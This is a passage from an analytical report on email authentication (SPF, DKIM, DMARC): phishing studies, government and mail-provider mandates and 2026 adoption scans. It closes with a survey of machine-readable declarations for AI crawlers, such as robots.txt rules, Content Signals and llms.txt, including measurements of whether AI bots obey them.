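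An SPF record can also be free of errors and still protect very little. Among domains with SPF, 34.7% approved more than 100,000 IP addresses, and nearly all of those domains had used "include" to adopt a mail provider's whole list. Microsoft's list covered 491,520 addresses, and almost 2.5 million domains included it. The hosting company OVH's list covered only two addresses.

A long list isn't dangerous if the provider controls which customer can use which domain. To test whether providers did this, the researchers rented web space from five hosting companies for about €30 and sent themselves mail under other people's domains. At four of the five, their mail could pass SPF for any domain that approved the company's servers. There were 26,095 such domains, including those of banks, political parties and health insurers. One company accounted for 24,959 of them. A strict DMARC policy would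 not necessarily have helped, since an SPF pass for the domain in the From address is enough to pass DMARC.

Warning the owners of faulty records achieved little. The researchers sent 111,951 emails, and two weeks later 3.3% of the errors were gone. The emails did not cover one type of error, in which a record refers to another that doesn't exist. By the study's counts, about 2.9% of those errors disappeared, compared with 3.6% of the errors the emails did cover. Most of the repairs might therefore have happened without the emails, although two weeks gave busy administrators little time to respond.

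### Mail that passes every check

An attacker who doesn't need Ana's exact address doesn't have to exploit any of these weaknesses. The simplest method is to register a lookalike domain, such as bakery-orders.example, and authenticate it, as spammers did with their own domains in 2004. The attacker can also open a free mail account and enter "Ana at the bakery" as the display name, the name shown beside the address. The message passes authentication because it does come from that account, and a hurried reader may look only at the name.

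An attacker who has stolen Ana's password can send mail from her real address. Her provider signs the message as usual, and it may appear in Ben's existing thread with her. Other attackers send mail through reputable companies, for example from a server rented from a large cloud service. This doesn't authenticate the message as coming from the bakery's domain, but receivers are reluctant to block the IP address it comes from.

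Luo, Young and colleagues (2024), in *Characterizing the Networks Sending Enterprise Phishing Emails*, looked for phishing in the mail of thousands of organisations that used the security company Barracuda. Their data covered January 2020, October 2020 and January 2021, and included more than 800,000 phishing messages and about 4 billion others, which they treated as clean. Barracuda's software had identified the phishing from the text and links, with an estimated precision of over 99%. In January 2020 the messages passed authentication at these rates:

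| Check | Clean mail that passed | Phishing that passed |
|---|---|---|
| SPF or DKIM | 39.6% | 23.3% |
| Both SPF and DKIM | 10.0% | 10.1% |
| DMARC | 30.0% | 10.4% |

The rates were similar in the two later months. Clean mail passed DMARC about three times as often as phishing did, so a pass was weak evidence that a message was clean. But a receiver could not have acted on a missing pass, because there were roughly 2 billion clean messages that January and only about 218,000 phishing messages. Refusing all mail without a DMARC pass would have stopped 90% of the phishing and 70% of the clean mail, or about 7,000 clean messages for every phishing message.

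The researchers then trained a program to separate phishing from clean mail using 12 features, and the authentication results were the least useful. The most useful were the amount of phishing the sending IP address had produced and the share of its mail that was phishing.

These figures probably understate the value of authentication, because the data contain only messages that reached an employee's account and exclude any forgery a receiver had already refused for failing DMARC. Three-quarters of the organisations also sent their incoming mail through an outside filter first. Such a filter can break SPF, as a forwarder can, which may partly explain why so little clean mail passed.

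Much of the phishing came from reputable networks. Amazon's and Microsoft's networks sent 31% of it, but also about 60% of the clean mail. One Amazon network address sent 1,324 phishing messages under 388 different sender addresses in a short burst in January 2021. Another, which probably belonged to a company with a hacked account, sent 115 phishing messages over about a week, along with at least 1,500 clean ones.

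Mail accounts at the big providers were a much smaller source. Fewer than 50 of the phishing messages came from the published addresses of Gmail or Outlook, and Luo and colleagues suggest that strict controls on outgoing mail may explain this. Gmail's engineers had described abuse of free accounts as a serious problem years earlier, so a provider that monitors its own customers may be able to stop abuse that authentication doesn't prevent.

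Recent records of each sender's behaviour also helped detect phishing. Barracuda added a detector that recalculated the reputation of every IP address each day, and over nearly five months it found 3% to 5% more phishing than the company's existing tools. It could still miss the fastest senders, such as the busiest addresses on one Russian hosting company's network, which sent all their phishing within 30 minutes.

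### Whether attackers had to change methods

Defenders of the standards accept that a scammer can authenticate a lookalike domain, but they argue that forging the exact domain has become harder, which pushes attackers towards methods that cost more or work less well. Archebelle-Smith writes that authentication raises the cost and complexity of impersonation "significantly", but gives no figures.

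There is good evidence that exact forgery became harder where both senders and receivers enforced the standards. In Hu and Wang's test, a "reject" policy cut the average success rate of forged mail from 60% to 13% at providers that ran all the checks, and to zero at most of them. The attacks that Chen and colleagues devised also took far more skill than typing a false address.

It is less clear that attackers moved elsewhere as a result. The best recent figure comes from *PiMRef* (Liu, Teoh and colleagues, 2025), a study of a new phishing detector. In PhishPot, an open collection of phishing messages, 90% imitated somebody from an account or domain that the attacker controlled, and 10% forged the sender's address. This is consistent with authentication having driven attackers away from forgery, but the study gives no earlier figure for comparison, so attackers may have preferred their own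 accounts all along. It also doesn't report how many of the messages passed SPF, DKIM or DMARC, so the 90% doesn't measure how much phishing passes authentication. Luo and colleagues' 10.4% is too old to provide a current figure.

The claim about cost is weaker still. Liu, Teoh and colleagues call imitation from the attacker's own account operationally cheaper than hacking a legitimate domain, because it requires only writing an email. But forging an unprotected address costs nothing, while a lookalike domain adds a small registration fee and a free account with a misleading display name adds no fee. Language models have also made the emails easier to write. Liu, Teoh and colleagues cite an industry report that found AI-generated content in 82.6% of phishing messages.

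An attacker also gains less if fewer people believe the message. Suppose a criminal sends 1,000 messages in the bakery's name, 600 reach an inbox, and one reader in ten falls for them, making 60 victims. After Ana publishes "reject", only 130 arrive, and the number of victims drops to 13. The criminal then switches to a lookalike domain. Again 600 messages arrive, but only one reader in twenty believes them, making 30 victims. Ana's policy cut the harm from exact forgeries by almost four-fifths, but the total harm by only half. If readers fell for the lookalike just as often, her policy would have achieved nothing. The 600 and the 130 follow Hu and Wang's averages, but the rates of belief are invented, and none of these studies measured the real ones.

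Attackers can also switch victims. If one bank enforces DMARC and another doesn't, a criminal may forge the second bank's address instead. The first bank's customers are safer, but total fraud may hardly change.

Authentication does make other defences possible. Liu, Teoh and colleagues built a detector that identifies the organisation a message claims to be from and checks the sender's domain against a list of that organisation's real domains. It raises an alarm if the domain isn't on the list and the message asks the reader to do something. In a test on real mail, it caught more than 80% of the phishing. The check is useful only if the sender's domain isn't forged, so the researchers rely on SPF, DKIM and DMARC to remove exact forgeries first. A message from a hacked account gets past both authentication and the detector, because the name and the domain match.

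## Mandates by governments and large mail providers, 2017 to 2026

Until 2017, domain owners who ignored SPF, DKIM and DMARC usually faced no consequences, as the administrators Hu and colleagues interviewed had noticed. The US government introduced consequences for its own agencies in October 2017, and Google and Yahoo did so for bulk senders in February 2024.

### The order to American agencies

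On 16 October 2017 the Department of Homeland Security issued Binding Operational Directive 18-01, which federal agencies must follow by law (Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency, *BOD 18-01*). Agencies had 90 days to publish SPF and DMARC records for every domain they had registered, with a DMARC policy of at least "none" and an address for reports. They had a year to change the policy to "reject". The order exempted national security systems and certain military and intelligence systems.

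The text mentions no fines. Each agency had to send DHS a plan within 30 days, a progress report at 60 days, and another every 30 days until it had finished. DHS also scanned the agencies' domains, and since DMARC records are public, an agency couldn't falsely claim to have one. The timetable gave agencies months to collect reports under a policy of "none" and find forgotten sources of mail before they risked losing legitimate mail.

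eWeek's *US Government Enforces DMARC Email Security Reject Policies* (2018) reports that the security company Agari found DMARC in use at 34% of agencies in November 2017, 47% in December and 81% by July 2018. The share with a policy of "reject" rose from 15% in January to 52% in July. Agari's founder, Patrick Peterson, said that publishing a policy of "none" takes five minutes and that the hard part is moving to "reject". He doubted that every agency would meet the October deadline, but an agency that missed it could still comply by giving DHS a written plan.

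Large companies were under no such order. In July 2018 about a third of the Fortune 500 had a DMARC policy, and 5% had reached "reject". These figures come from Agari, which sold DMARC services and had an interest in promoting them, and big companies may use more outside mailing firms than agencies do. Still, it is hard to see what besides the order could have more than tripled the agencies' use of "reject" in six months.

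Figures for all .gov domains are less useful as evidence of the directive's effect, because they include state and local governments, which the directive doesn't cover. DMARCguard's *Email Authentication 2026* (2026), a scan by a company that sells DMARC monitoring, found a DMARC record on 76.4% of 3,746 .gov domains and credited the directive. Yet .edu domains, which are under no federal order of this kind, had a higher rate, at 84.0%. A "reject" policy was more common on .gov domains, at 33%, than on .edu domains, at 18%.

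### Countries with and without a mandate

*The Coverage Gap* (Mellafe, 2026) compares Chile with countries whose governments had pressed public bodies to adopt DMARC. Chile's cybersecurity law took effect in January 2025, but the instructions its new agency issued that December mention none of the three standards, and the government has published only voluntary advice. Mellafe puts DMARC adoption at roughly 12% of Chilean government domains, compared with more than 95% in the other countries after their mandates.

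Both numbers are weaker evidence than they seem. The 12% comes from a 2024 study by PowerDMARC, a company that sells DMARC services. Mellafe's own audit, in May 2026, covered a different group, 915 organisations that Chile has designated as vital, many of them private companies. The audit found faulty email authentication at 84% of these organisations, but it counted a DMARC policy of "none" as a fault, so the 84% can't be converted into an adoption rate.

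For the United States, Mellafe reports a rise from about 14% when DHS issued the directive to over 91% within eighteen months, and eventually to over 99%. The passage cites only the directive, which predates the later figures. Agari's figure of 34% one month after the directive is hard to reconcile with a start of 14%, unless agencies moved very fast in the first weeks or the two counts covered different domains. For Denmark, the paper's summary table gives "over 90%" rather than over 95%. The same table presents the American, British and Dutch percentages as the share of organisations with a published contact for security problems, which is a different measure from DMARC adoption.

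Mellafe acknowledges that the countries counted different things, from about 440 American agency domains to about 6,000 names under gov.uk, and that governments supplied some of the figures themselves. The gap is wide enough that better data would probably still show it, but compulsion may not be the only cause. Britain also gave public bodies a free service that checked their settings and processed their DMARC reports, and the Dutch government let its departments decline DMARC if they publicly explained why. The American record is better evidence for the effect of an order because it covers agencies before and after the order, with the Fortune 500 for comparison.

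### Google and Yahoo make authentication a condition of delivery

A government can give orders to its own agencies, but a large mail provider can set terms for anyone who wants to reach its users. In 2022 Google began to require some form of authentication on all mail to Gmail. On 3 October 2023 Kumaran (2023), in *New Gmail protections for a safer, less spammy inbox*, announced stricter rules for bulk senders. Yahoo adopted similar ones. Google's *Email sender guidelines* set out what senders have had to do since 1 February 2024:

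| | Everyone who writes to Gmail users | Bulk senders |
|---|---|---|
| SPF and DKIM | At least one | Both |
| DMARC record | Not required | Required, but the policy can be "none" |
| From address | Must not imitate a Gmail address | Must also align with the SPF or DKIM domain |
| Spam reports by users | Below 0.3% | Below 0.3% |
| Marketing mail | No special rule | One-click unsubscribe |

Google's *Email sender guidelines FAQ* defines a bulk sender as one that sends close to 5,000 messages or more to personal Gmail accounts within 24 hours. Suppose Ana's bakery has grown into a chain, and one December day it sends a newsletter to 3,000 Gmail users from bakery.example and 2,500 order confirmations from shop.bakery.example. Google adds the two together, and the total of 5,500 permanently makes the bakery a bulk sender. Yahoo gives no number, but Marcel Becker, a product director there, told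 the email delivery company Mailgun that any organisation that regularly sends mass messages should consider itself a bulk sender.

Google phased in the penalties. In February 2024 it began returning temporary errors for a small portion of the mail that broke the rules, and in April it began rejecting some of that mail, according to TechRadar's *Gmail is getting tough on spam*. After a temporary error, the sending server tries again later, so the message is delayed but not lost, and the error code identifies the missing requirement. Since November 2025 Google has enforced the rules more strictly, with both temporary and permanent rejections.

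Bulk mail without SPF and DKIM, or with a From address that doesn't align, risks rejection or the spam folder. The only penalty Google lists for a missing DMARC record is losing help with delivery problems, although there is also a temporary error code for it.

Google doesn't say why it accepts a policy of "none", but its other rules suggest that it mainly needed a reliable way to tell which domain a message came from. Gmail had been scoring domains by their behaviour since at least 2006, and a score is useful only if the mail really comes from the domain. Alignment on the messages that pass is enough to establish that, and the DMARC policy applies only to messages that fail. Domain owners had held back for fear of losing genuine mail, which "none" can't cause. If Google had required "reject", senders would have risked losing mail at every receiver that followed the policy, not only at Gmail.

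However, accepting "none" left a large gap in protection. When a message fails DMARC, Gmail generally follows the policy of the domain in the From address. A company whose policy is "none" has met Google's requirement, but it hasn't asked mail providers to block messages that forge its domain.

Google also exempted forwarded mail and mailing-list posts from the alignment requirement. Yahoo had made no such exception in 2014, when its strict policy disrupted mailing lists. Google asks operators of lists and forwarding services to add ARC headers, which record whether a message passed its checks on arrival.

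### Microsoft follows in 2025

*Strengthening Email Ecosystem* (Puneeth, 2025) announced Microsoft's own requirements for bulk senders on 2 April 2025. Since 5 May 2025, domains that send more than 5,000 messages a day to consumer addresses at Outlook.com, Hotmail and Live have needed SPF, DKIM and DMARC. Under Microsoft's *Policies, Practices, and Guidelines*, mail that doesn't meet the requirements goes to the junk folder, and Microsoft may reject it if the sender doesn't fix the problem. Senders of rejected mail get an error about the domain in their From address, which Microsoft explains in *Fix NDR error "550 5.7.515" in Outlook.com*.

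According to EasyDMARC, which sells DMARC services, Microsoft refuses mail from large senders if it fails authentication, even when their DMARC policy is "none". This in effect replaces the domain owner's policy with Microsoft's stricter rule, which should also stop some forgeries of large senders that never chose to enforce DMARC.

Enforcement can also stop genuine mail. In a comment on Microsoft's *Strengthening Email Ecosystem*, a customer described buying event tickets with a personal address that had forwarded mail for more than 20 years and now forwarded to an Outlook.com account. The ticket company's first two messages arrived, but the one with the link to open the tickets never did. The customer blamed the new rule but had not seen an error that would confirm this. The explanation is plausible because forwarding breaks SPF, and the missing message may have come from a different server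 without a valid DKIM signature.

### What Google's figures count

In Google's October 2023 announcement, Kumaran wrote that the number of unauthenticated messages Gmail users received fell by 75% after the 2022 rule. That drop includes messages Gmail refused, and those refusals would reduce the number delivered even if no sender changed anything.

Kumaran gave the results of the 2024 rules to the journalist Davey Winder in October 2024, shortly before Google presented them at an industry conference. Winder's Forbes article, reposted by mundo1phone as *Google Confirms New Gmail Security Boost For 2.5 Billion Users* (2024), reports 65% fewer unauthenticated messages sent to Gmail users, 265 billion fewer such messages in 2024, and 50% more bulk senders following good practice. Valimail's *Google stats show why DMARC and email authentication matter* repeats the Forbes numbers, so it doesn't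 independently confirm them.

These figures refer to messages sent, so they are better evidence that senders changed. If the 65% and the 265 billion cover the same period, Gmail received about 143 billion unauthenticated messages instead of about 408 billion. Kumaran wrote in 2023 that Gmail blocks nearly 15 billion unwanted messages a day, so 265 billion is about as many as it blocks in 18 days.

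None of the figures measure fraud. The count of unauthenticated messages can fall because an honest company published its records, a forger gave up, or a spammer bought a domain and authenticated its mail. If that spammer sends as many messages as before, Google's count improves but users get just as much spam. Phishing that passes every check doesn't appear in the figures.

Google has published one number closer to what users care about. Wen (2024) reported in *Email scams surge over the holiday* that Gmail users had flagged 35% fewer scams in the first month of the holiday season than a year earlier. Wen credited security features launched that year, including a language model that blocked 20% more spam, and didn't mention the sender rules. The rules may have helped the filters by making senders easier to identify, but these numbers don't separate the effect of the rules from that of the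 new features.

### How a penalty ends the stall

Ozment and Schechter's model of adoption can be extended with a penalty for not adopting. In the earlier example, adopting costs each of ten companies that send mail 3 and brings it 1 for every other adopter, so none wants to go first. Now suppose that each company's mail is worth 10 to it, and that 40% of the mail goes to users of one large receiver, which announces that it will refuse unauthenticated mail. A company that doesn't adopt now loses 4, which is more than the 3 it costs to adopt. Each company therefore adopts even if no other does, so adoption no longer depends on reaching a critical mass.

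In general, a company adopts when *bᵢ(A) + s·vᵢ > cᵢ*. The benefit *bᵢ(A)* and the cost *cᵢ* are the same as before. In the new term, *s·vᵢ*, *vᵢ* is the value of the company's mail and *s* is the share of that mail sent to receivers that impose the penalty. With these numbers, the first company adopts only if *s* is above 30%. A receiver with 10% of the mail imposes a loss of 1, which lowers the critical mass from four companies to three but isn't enough to make any company adopt first.

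A small receiver that refuses unauthenticated mail also hurts itself, because senders don't change and its users keep losing mail they want. If a large receiver does the same, most senders adopt authentication quickly and its users lose mail only temporarily. Two receivers with a 20% share each could succeed together where either would fail alone, so it mattered that Google and Yahoo announced their rules at the same time. A few companies can coordinate this way much more easily than millions of domain owners can.

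The penalty also has to be likely enough to make adoption worthwhile. If the large receiver refuses only a quarter of the unauthenticated mail, the expected loss falls from 4 to 1, and the first company does not adopt. This is a reason to expect Gmail's stricter enforcement since November 2025 to increase adoption more than the temporary errors of early 2024. Small senders may still not adopt. If a company's mail is worth only 2, losing 40% of it means a loss of 0.8, which is less than the cost of adopting.

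By the same reasoning, most companies will probably stop at "none". Suppose that moving from "none" to "reject" costs another 5 in staff time and lost mail. A bank that criminals often impersonate might gain 7 from the move, and a bakery 1. Google imposes no penalty for staying at "none", so only the bank moves. The American directive did put pressure on agencies that stayed at "none", and within nine months half of them had reached "reject". The costs and gains in the example are invented, so it shows why a penalty would move more companies to "reject", but not how many.

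### Adoption and enforcement in 2026

The new rules reached many people who had never heard of DMARC, as the email delivery blog Spam Resource noted (*2024*, 2025). Valimail, which also sells DMARC services, saw 2.5 million domains add authentication or DMARC records in the first 60 days of 2024. It reported that most email marketers chose the policy "none" and left out the address for reports. In Mailgun's later survey, 37% of senders were not familiar with the requirements.

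Raw counts of new DMARC records can mislead. *DMARC policy growth 2020 through 2025* (2026), from the group behind DMARC, describes surges, some in the millions of records, that mostly disappeared over the following quarters. Some came from a single entry that covered tens of thousands of names, including names of routers and network switches. Scanning a fixed list of domains avoids much of this problem. EasyDMARC's *2026 DMARC Adoption & Enforcement Report* (2026) found valid records on 29.1% of the top 1.8 million domains in 2023 and on 52.1% in early 2026.

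Four other scans from 2026 give enforcement rates. Companies ran all four, and several of these companies sell email security or monitoring. One scan is DMARCguard's. The other three appear in Berezin's *Two Providers, a Stubborn Plateau and a Very Long Tail* (2026); McCabe's *DMARC Has Been Public Since 2012* (2026), which uses data from the security company CipherCue; and CircleID's *Publishing DMARC Is Not the Same as Operating It*, in which Samuel Chenard presents data from the company Palisade.

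| Scan | Sample | Publish DMARC | Enforce it, share of all domains | Enforce it, share of publishers |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| DMARCguard, February | 5.5 million ranked domains | 30.4% | 12.8% | 42.0% |
| Berezin, July | Top million domains | about 46% | about 22% | 46.9% |
| McCabe, April to July | 67,336 company domains | 54.9% | 31.5% | 57.4% |
| CircleID, August | 99,310 domains from a fixed list | 58.1% | 37.2% | 64.0% |

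The figures range from 30% to 58% mainly because the samples differ. DMARCguard's long list includes millions of obscure websites, many of which may never send mail. Among the 10,000 most visited domains, it found DMARC on 62.5%. McCabe warns that CipherCue's sample includes only domains the company tracks and doesn't represent companies worldwide. Berezin, who works for an email marketing company, used public data from the University of Twente and its partners, and counted a policy as enforced only if it applied to all failing mail.

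Berezin's sample is the closest match to the one Hu and Wang scanned in October 2017, when 4.6% of the top million domains published DMARC and 1.0% enforced it. The two lists of popular domains differ somewhat, but the share publishing DMARC has grown about tenfold in nine years and the share enforcing it about twentyfold.

Berezin nevertheless argues that the 2024 rules increased publication but not enforcement. The records support the claim about publication. The most common one, on 58,064 domains, is `v=DMARC1; p=none;`, and another 32,682 domains have the same text without the last semicolon. Together they make up a fifth of the DMARC records in the scan. They contain no address for reports, so the domain owners won't receive the information they would need to move to enforcement.

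The second half is less certain. Berezin points out that the share of DMARC publishers that enforce it isn't rising, and fell by 0.44 percentage points in the latest 30 days. But new records with "none" lower that share even if nobody weakens a policy. If 50 of 100 publishers enforce and 20 more domains join at "none", the share falls from 50% to 42%. If five of the newcomers then move to "reject", the share is still only 46%, even though 55 domains now enforce DMARC. The share could therefore fall while the rules slowly brought in new enforcers.

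McCabe thinks owners stay at "none" because they can't tell which machines are sending their mail. That agrees with what administrators told Hu and colleagues, but McCabe's evidence for it is poor. The scan found that domain owners have their reports sent to 10,268 different domains, 79% of which appear only once. Counting the domains that receive reports doesn't measure how hard it is to recognise the senders listed in the reports.

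DMARC joined the IETF's standards track in May 2026, as RFC 9989. By then, Gmail and Yahoo had required bulk senders to use it for more than two years, and Outlook.com had required it for one year.

### Who decides what gets delivered

The penalty worked because so much mail goes to a few companies, and that concentration has grown. Berezin found that 44.6% of popular domains with mail service ran their own mail server in 2016, but only 22.4% did in July 2026. Google now receives mail for 21.8% of all these domains and Microsoft for 16.8%, while the next largest company Berezin could identify has 1.9%. Google's sender rules apply only to personal accounts, not to the business accounts on these domains, but its filters handle both.

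Gamba and colleagues argue that inboxes improved while the ability to contest filtering collapsed, and they place much of the blame on where the industry makes its decisions. They single out M3AAWG, the trade body formerly called MAAWG, where the large providers and other companies coordinate delivery standards. M3AAWG restricts membership and does not make its proceedings public, so most of the senders whose mail depends on those standards have no say in them. Google presented its 2024 results at an M3AAWG conference. Gamba and colleagues call this pattern "depoliticization," meaning that a choice people could dispute becomes a technical specification and no longer looks like a choice.

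The 2024 rules only partly fit this account. Google published them four months in advance, and they rely on open standards. A sender whose mail breaks them gets a code that identifies the fault, which is more than a private spam classifier provides. But Google wrote the rules and can change them. It warns in its FAQ that it will probably require alignment with both SPF and DKIM one day. Microsoft revised its penalty on 29 April 2025, six days before its rules took effect. Mail can also meet every requirement and still land in the spam folder.

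The providers have a good case for their requirements. Kumaran argued that badly configured bulk senders let attackers hide among them, and that because the requirements follow open standards, everyone who uses email benefits when a sender meets them. A company that adds DKIM to satisfy Gmail also makes its mail easier to check at Ben's school. The strictest rules apply to large senders, who are best able to do the work, and Kumaran noted that many already met most of them. Voluntary adoption had also been slow. Fourteen years after Wong wrote SPF, fewer than half of the top million domains had a valid SPF record.

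That case is convincing for authentication, where the voluntary approach had stalled and complying took modest effort. It is less convincing for decisions that senders can't check. Sean Kamath, who runs two mail servers for family members, commented on Berezin's article that Google usually marks their mail as spam and that Hotmail says the servers are on a blocklist. Berezin replied that this normally means Microsoft's internal list. He said senders can request removal through an online form but sometimes get no answer or only a stock reply. Kamath had considered a stricter DMARC policy but feared it would make delivery worse.

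Gamba and colleagues contrast this with financial regulation in the United States. When the Securities and Exchange Commission writes a rule for investment advisers, it must accept public comments, and those affected can challenge the rule in court. They concede that industries can capture regulators too. Even so, an adviser can object through these channels, while Kamath has only a web form.

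## Content declarations for AI readers, 2024 to 2026

Website owners now publish requests and statements for AI systems. As with a DMARC policy, the recipient may follow or ignore them. Most protect publishers by asking AI companies not to collect a page or train a model on it. Others help a machine read a site or find out where a picture came from. Very few protect an agent from hostile text on the page it is reading, which was the purpose of the declarations Franklin and colleagues proposed.

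Chowdhury (2026), in *terms.txt*, compares many of these declarations while proposing another, and specification.website's *Agent Readiness* lists them for site owners. In late 2026 the main ones stood as follows:

| Declaration | What the owner publishes | Whom it mainly serves | Who has to act on it | Status |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| robots.txt | `Disallow: /` under a crawler's name | Publisher | Companies that run crawlers | IETF standard since 2022 |
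| Content Signals | `Content-Signal: search=yes, ai-train=no` | Publisher | AI companies | Cloudflare's convention |
| AI Preferences | Terms such as `train-ai` and `search` | Publisher | AI companies | IETF drafts |
| TDMRep | A `tdm-reservation` field | Publisher | Anyone who mines text or data | Optional convention |
| llms.txt | A list of the site's main pages | Publisher and AI reader | Agent operators | Community convention, version 2 |
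| C2PA | A signed record of a media file's origin | Anyone who views the file | Makers of software that displays it | Published standard |
| Untrusted label | `data-untrusted="true"` on part of a page | Agent's user | Agent operators | Research prototype |

### Rules for AI crawlers in robots.txt

The robots.txt file dates from 1994, when most automated visitors were search engines' crawlers, programs that follow links and download pages. Suppose Ana wants to keep OpenAI's crawler GPTBot, which collects training data, off the bakery's website but let everyone else in. She publishes this:

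```
User-agent: GPTBot
Disallow: /

User-agent: *
Allow: /
```

A crawler that follows the standard fetches this file first, looks for its own name and obeys the rules below it. The visitor supplies that name, just as the sender of an email supplies the From address, and the file gives Ana no way to check it. A scraper can therefore call itself Googlebot and take whatever Googlebot is allowed to take.

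Publishers adopted these rules quickly once they learned that AI companies were training on their pages. Chowdhury reports that Longpre and colleagues audited 14,000 domains whose text appears in three large training collections. Between April 2023 and April 2024, the share of text in those collections covered by rules against AI crawlers rose from almost nothing to more than 5%. For the most actively maintained domains, the share was over a quarter. Many sites' terms of service forbade something their robots.txt allowed. Some sites also shut out archives and researchers by accident, because the format cannot distinguish a commercial training crawler from a library's.

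### Whether crawlers obey

*Scrapers selectively respect robots.txt directives* (Kim, Bock and colleagues, 2025) tested whether bots obeyed robots.txt on a busy website at the researchers' own university, Duke. In early 2025, the researchers used four versions of the file on the site for two weeks each. The first, the site's original, allowed nearly everything and served as a control. The second asked bots to wait 30 seconds between pages, the third limited most bots to a single section of the site, and the fourth banned most bots from every page. At the university's request, the researchers exempted eight bots, including Googlebot and Bing's crawler, from the third and fourth versions, so the study did not test whether those eight obey a ban.

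For each bot, they calculated the share of its requests that kept to the rules. Under the total ban, the only request a bot could properly make was for robots.txt itself. Average compliance was 62% for the delay, 31% for the single section and 26% for the total ban. The 62% is flattering, since many bots had already been waiting that long before anyone asked them to. Some well-known AI bots behaved very differently from others:

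| Bot | Company | Company promised to obey | Kept to the one open section | Obeyed the total ban |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| ClaudeBot | Anthropic | Yes | 100% | 100% |
| Amazonbot | Amazon | Yes | 100% | 100% |
| GPTBot | OpenAI | Yes | 31% | 100% |
| ChatGPT-User | OpenAI | Yes | 13% | 100% |
| Applebot | Apple | Yes | 44% | 4% |
| PerplexityBot | Perplexity | No | 90% | 20% |
| Bytespider | ByteDance | No | 0% | 3% |

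ChatGPT-User, which fetches pages for people using ChatGPT, mostly ignored the partial ban and then fully obeyed the total one. Part of the reason may be that bots were slow to check for new rules. On three other sites, fewer than 40% of the AI assistants and AI search crawlers fetched robots.txt at least once a week, so a bot could follow an old version for much of a two-week test. Impostors may also have lowered some scores, since Kim and colleagues found signs of bots using other bots' names.

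The measure can also understate compliance, because a bot that already knew of the ban and stayed away made no requests to count. But the lowest scores came from software that rarely identifies its owner. Headless browsers, which run without a visible window and are popular with scrapers, complied with the total ban in 1% of their requests.

An earlier and much smaller test, described by Kim and colleagues, looks more encouraging. Seven AI bots visited a site. The operators of six had promised to obey robots.txt, and all six bots did. The operator of the seventh, Bytespider, had made no such promise. *Is Misinformation More Open?* (2025) summarises earlier research as finding that the major AI crawlers generally respect the file. These results are consistent with each other if well-known companies mostly obey robots.txt and other crawler operators don't. There are exceptions even among known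 companies. In August 2025 Cloudflare accused Perplexity of using undeclared names and changing networks to fetch pages from sites that had banned its crawler.

These measurements all date from 2025 or earlier, and companies have since renamed and split their crawlers. The measurements are better evidence that compliance varies by company than of how any one company behaves today.

### Preferences about what happens to the text

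A rule in robots.txt covers collection and is silent about use. Ana may be happy for a customer's assistant to read her prices but not want her recipes in a training set. In September 2025 Cloudflare (2025) introduced Content Signals, an extra line in robots.txt for this purpose:

```
Content-Signal: search=yes, ai-input=yes, ai-train=no
```

Here *search* means building a search index and showing links with short excerpts. *ai-input* means giving the page to a model while it answers someone, and *ai-train* means training a model on it. If Ana leaves a term out, she neither grants nor refuses permission for that use. The accompanying text presents any refusal as a reservation of rights under European copyright law. Cloudflare admits that some companies might ignore the signals, and advises publishers who want control to block unwanted bots as well.

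Content Signals spread faster than any of the email standards. At the launch, Cloudflare said it would add `search=yes, ai-train=no` to the robots.txt files it already managed for customers on more than 3.8 million domains. Those owners had chosen to refuse training, so the line reflects a real preference, but the number of domains mostly reflects Cloudflare's reach. In July 2026 Cloudflare added `use=reference` to the same files. Lee and Becker's *Your site, your rules* explains that this term permits indexing, excerpts and links but not full reproduction. Its presence on millions of domains would reflect a default setting, much as many DMARC records reflect the least that Google would accept.

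Cloudflare can also penalize a bot that it catches abusing the signals. The bot loses its "Verified" status, which Cloudflare's customers can use to admit bots by category. More than 20% of web domains use Cloudflare, so the loss would hurt a search engine or a large AI company, but it would affect a scraper that never identified itself less.

The hardest case is a crawler that works for both search and AI. According to Cloudflare's *Content Independence Day, one year on*, these crawlers made up over 36% of the crawler activity the company could classify in June 2026. A publisher that blocks Googlebot to keep its content out of AI also disappears from Google Search, which supplies about 88% of referral traffic, according to figures Chowdhury cites. Lee and Becker announced that from 15 September 2026 Cloudflare would treat Googlebot, Applebot and Bing's crawler as training crawlers, and block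 them for customers who had chosen to block training. On that day, the company offered a gentler option, described in *Have it both ways* (2026), that lets a site refuse training and stay in search.

That option depends on the crawlers' owners keeping a promise. Southern (2026) reported in *Cloudflare Lets Sites Disallow AI Training Without Blocking Googlebot* that Google and Apple honoured such refusals and that Bing's support through robots.txt was still pending. A site's owner cannot confirm this, because the server's logs record only that Googlebot fetched a page, not whether Google then indexed it or trained on it. Outside researchers can therefore measure compliance with `Disallow` but not with `ai-train=no`.

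The IETF has been trying to agree on a common vocabulary since before Cloudflare published its own. Its AI Preferences group planned to submit a standard for publication in August 2026, according to the record for *A Vocabulary For Expressing AI Usage Preferences* (Keller and Thomson, 2025). But the group did not reach consensus in a call for final approval, and the chairs cut the draft back to a "Minimum Viable Product", according to the group's notes. The minutes of a spring 2026 IETF meeting record co-chair Mark Nottingham saying that the group had removed many contentious terms and made little progress between meetings. In August 2026, *AI Preference Vocabulary* (Keller and Thomson, 2026) still carried a warning that the draft did not reflect the group's consensus.

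A companion draft would let sites put these preferences in robots.txt or in the header sent with each page. The group's charter rules out enforcement, so even a finished standard would only give Ana a clearer way to state her preferences. The dispute between SPF and Sender ID also delayed a standard, but receivers could use SPF without one because they could check whether a message passed. An AI company has less reason to adopt a vocabulary early, because doing so only restricts the company itself.

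TDMRep is a narrower declaration, which states whether a site's owner reserves the right to object to text and data mining. The owner puts a `tdm-reservation` field in a page's header, in the page itself or in a file on the site. specification.website describes its force as "legal, not technical". It could help a publisher who sues, since the company could not easily argue that it had no notice of the objection. But the publisher first has to find out that the company mined the text, and then pay for a lawyer.

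Chowdhury wants to turn these requests into conditions. Under terms.txt, a site's file might contain `Purpose: train-ai deny` for its paid articles and a price per request for its free ones. The site's server would then refuse any crawler that failed to sign its request, state its purpose or pay where required. In a prototype, these checks added less than a millisecond per request. The signature lets a publisher who later discovers a false statement of purpose identify who made it, but it doesn't prove that a stated purpose is true. A scraper that refuses to sign can still take whatever the site leaves open to the public. The proposal comes from one independent researcher and has no reported users.

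### Declarations that help machines read or trace content

Some owners want more AI visitors. They can publish llms.txt, a short text file that lists a site's most useful pages with a note on each. Ana's might contain:

```
# Ana's Bakery
- [Prices](/prices.md): bread and cakes, updated weekly
- [Orders](/orders.md): how to order a birthday cake
```

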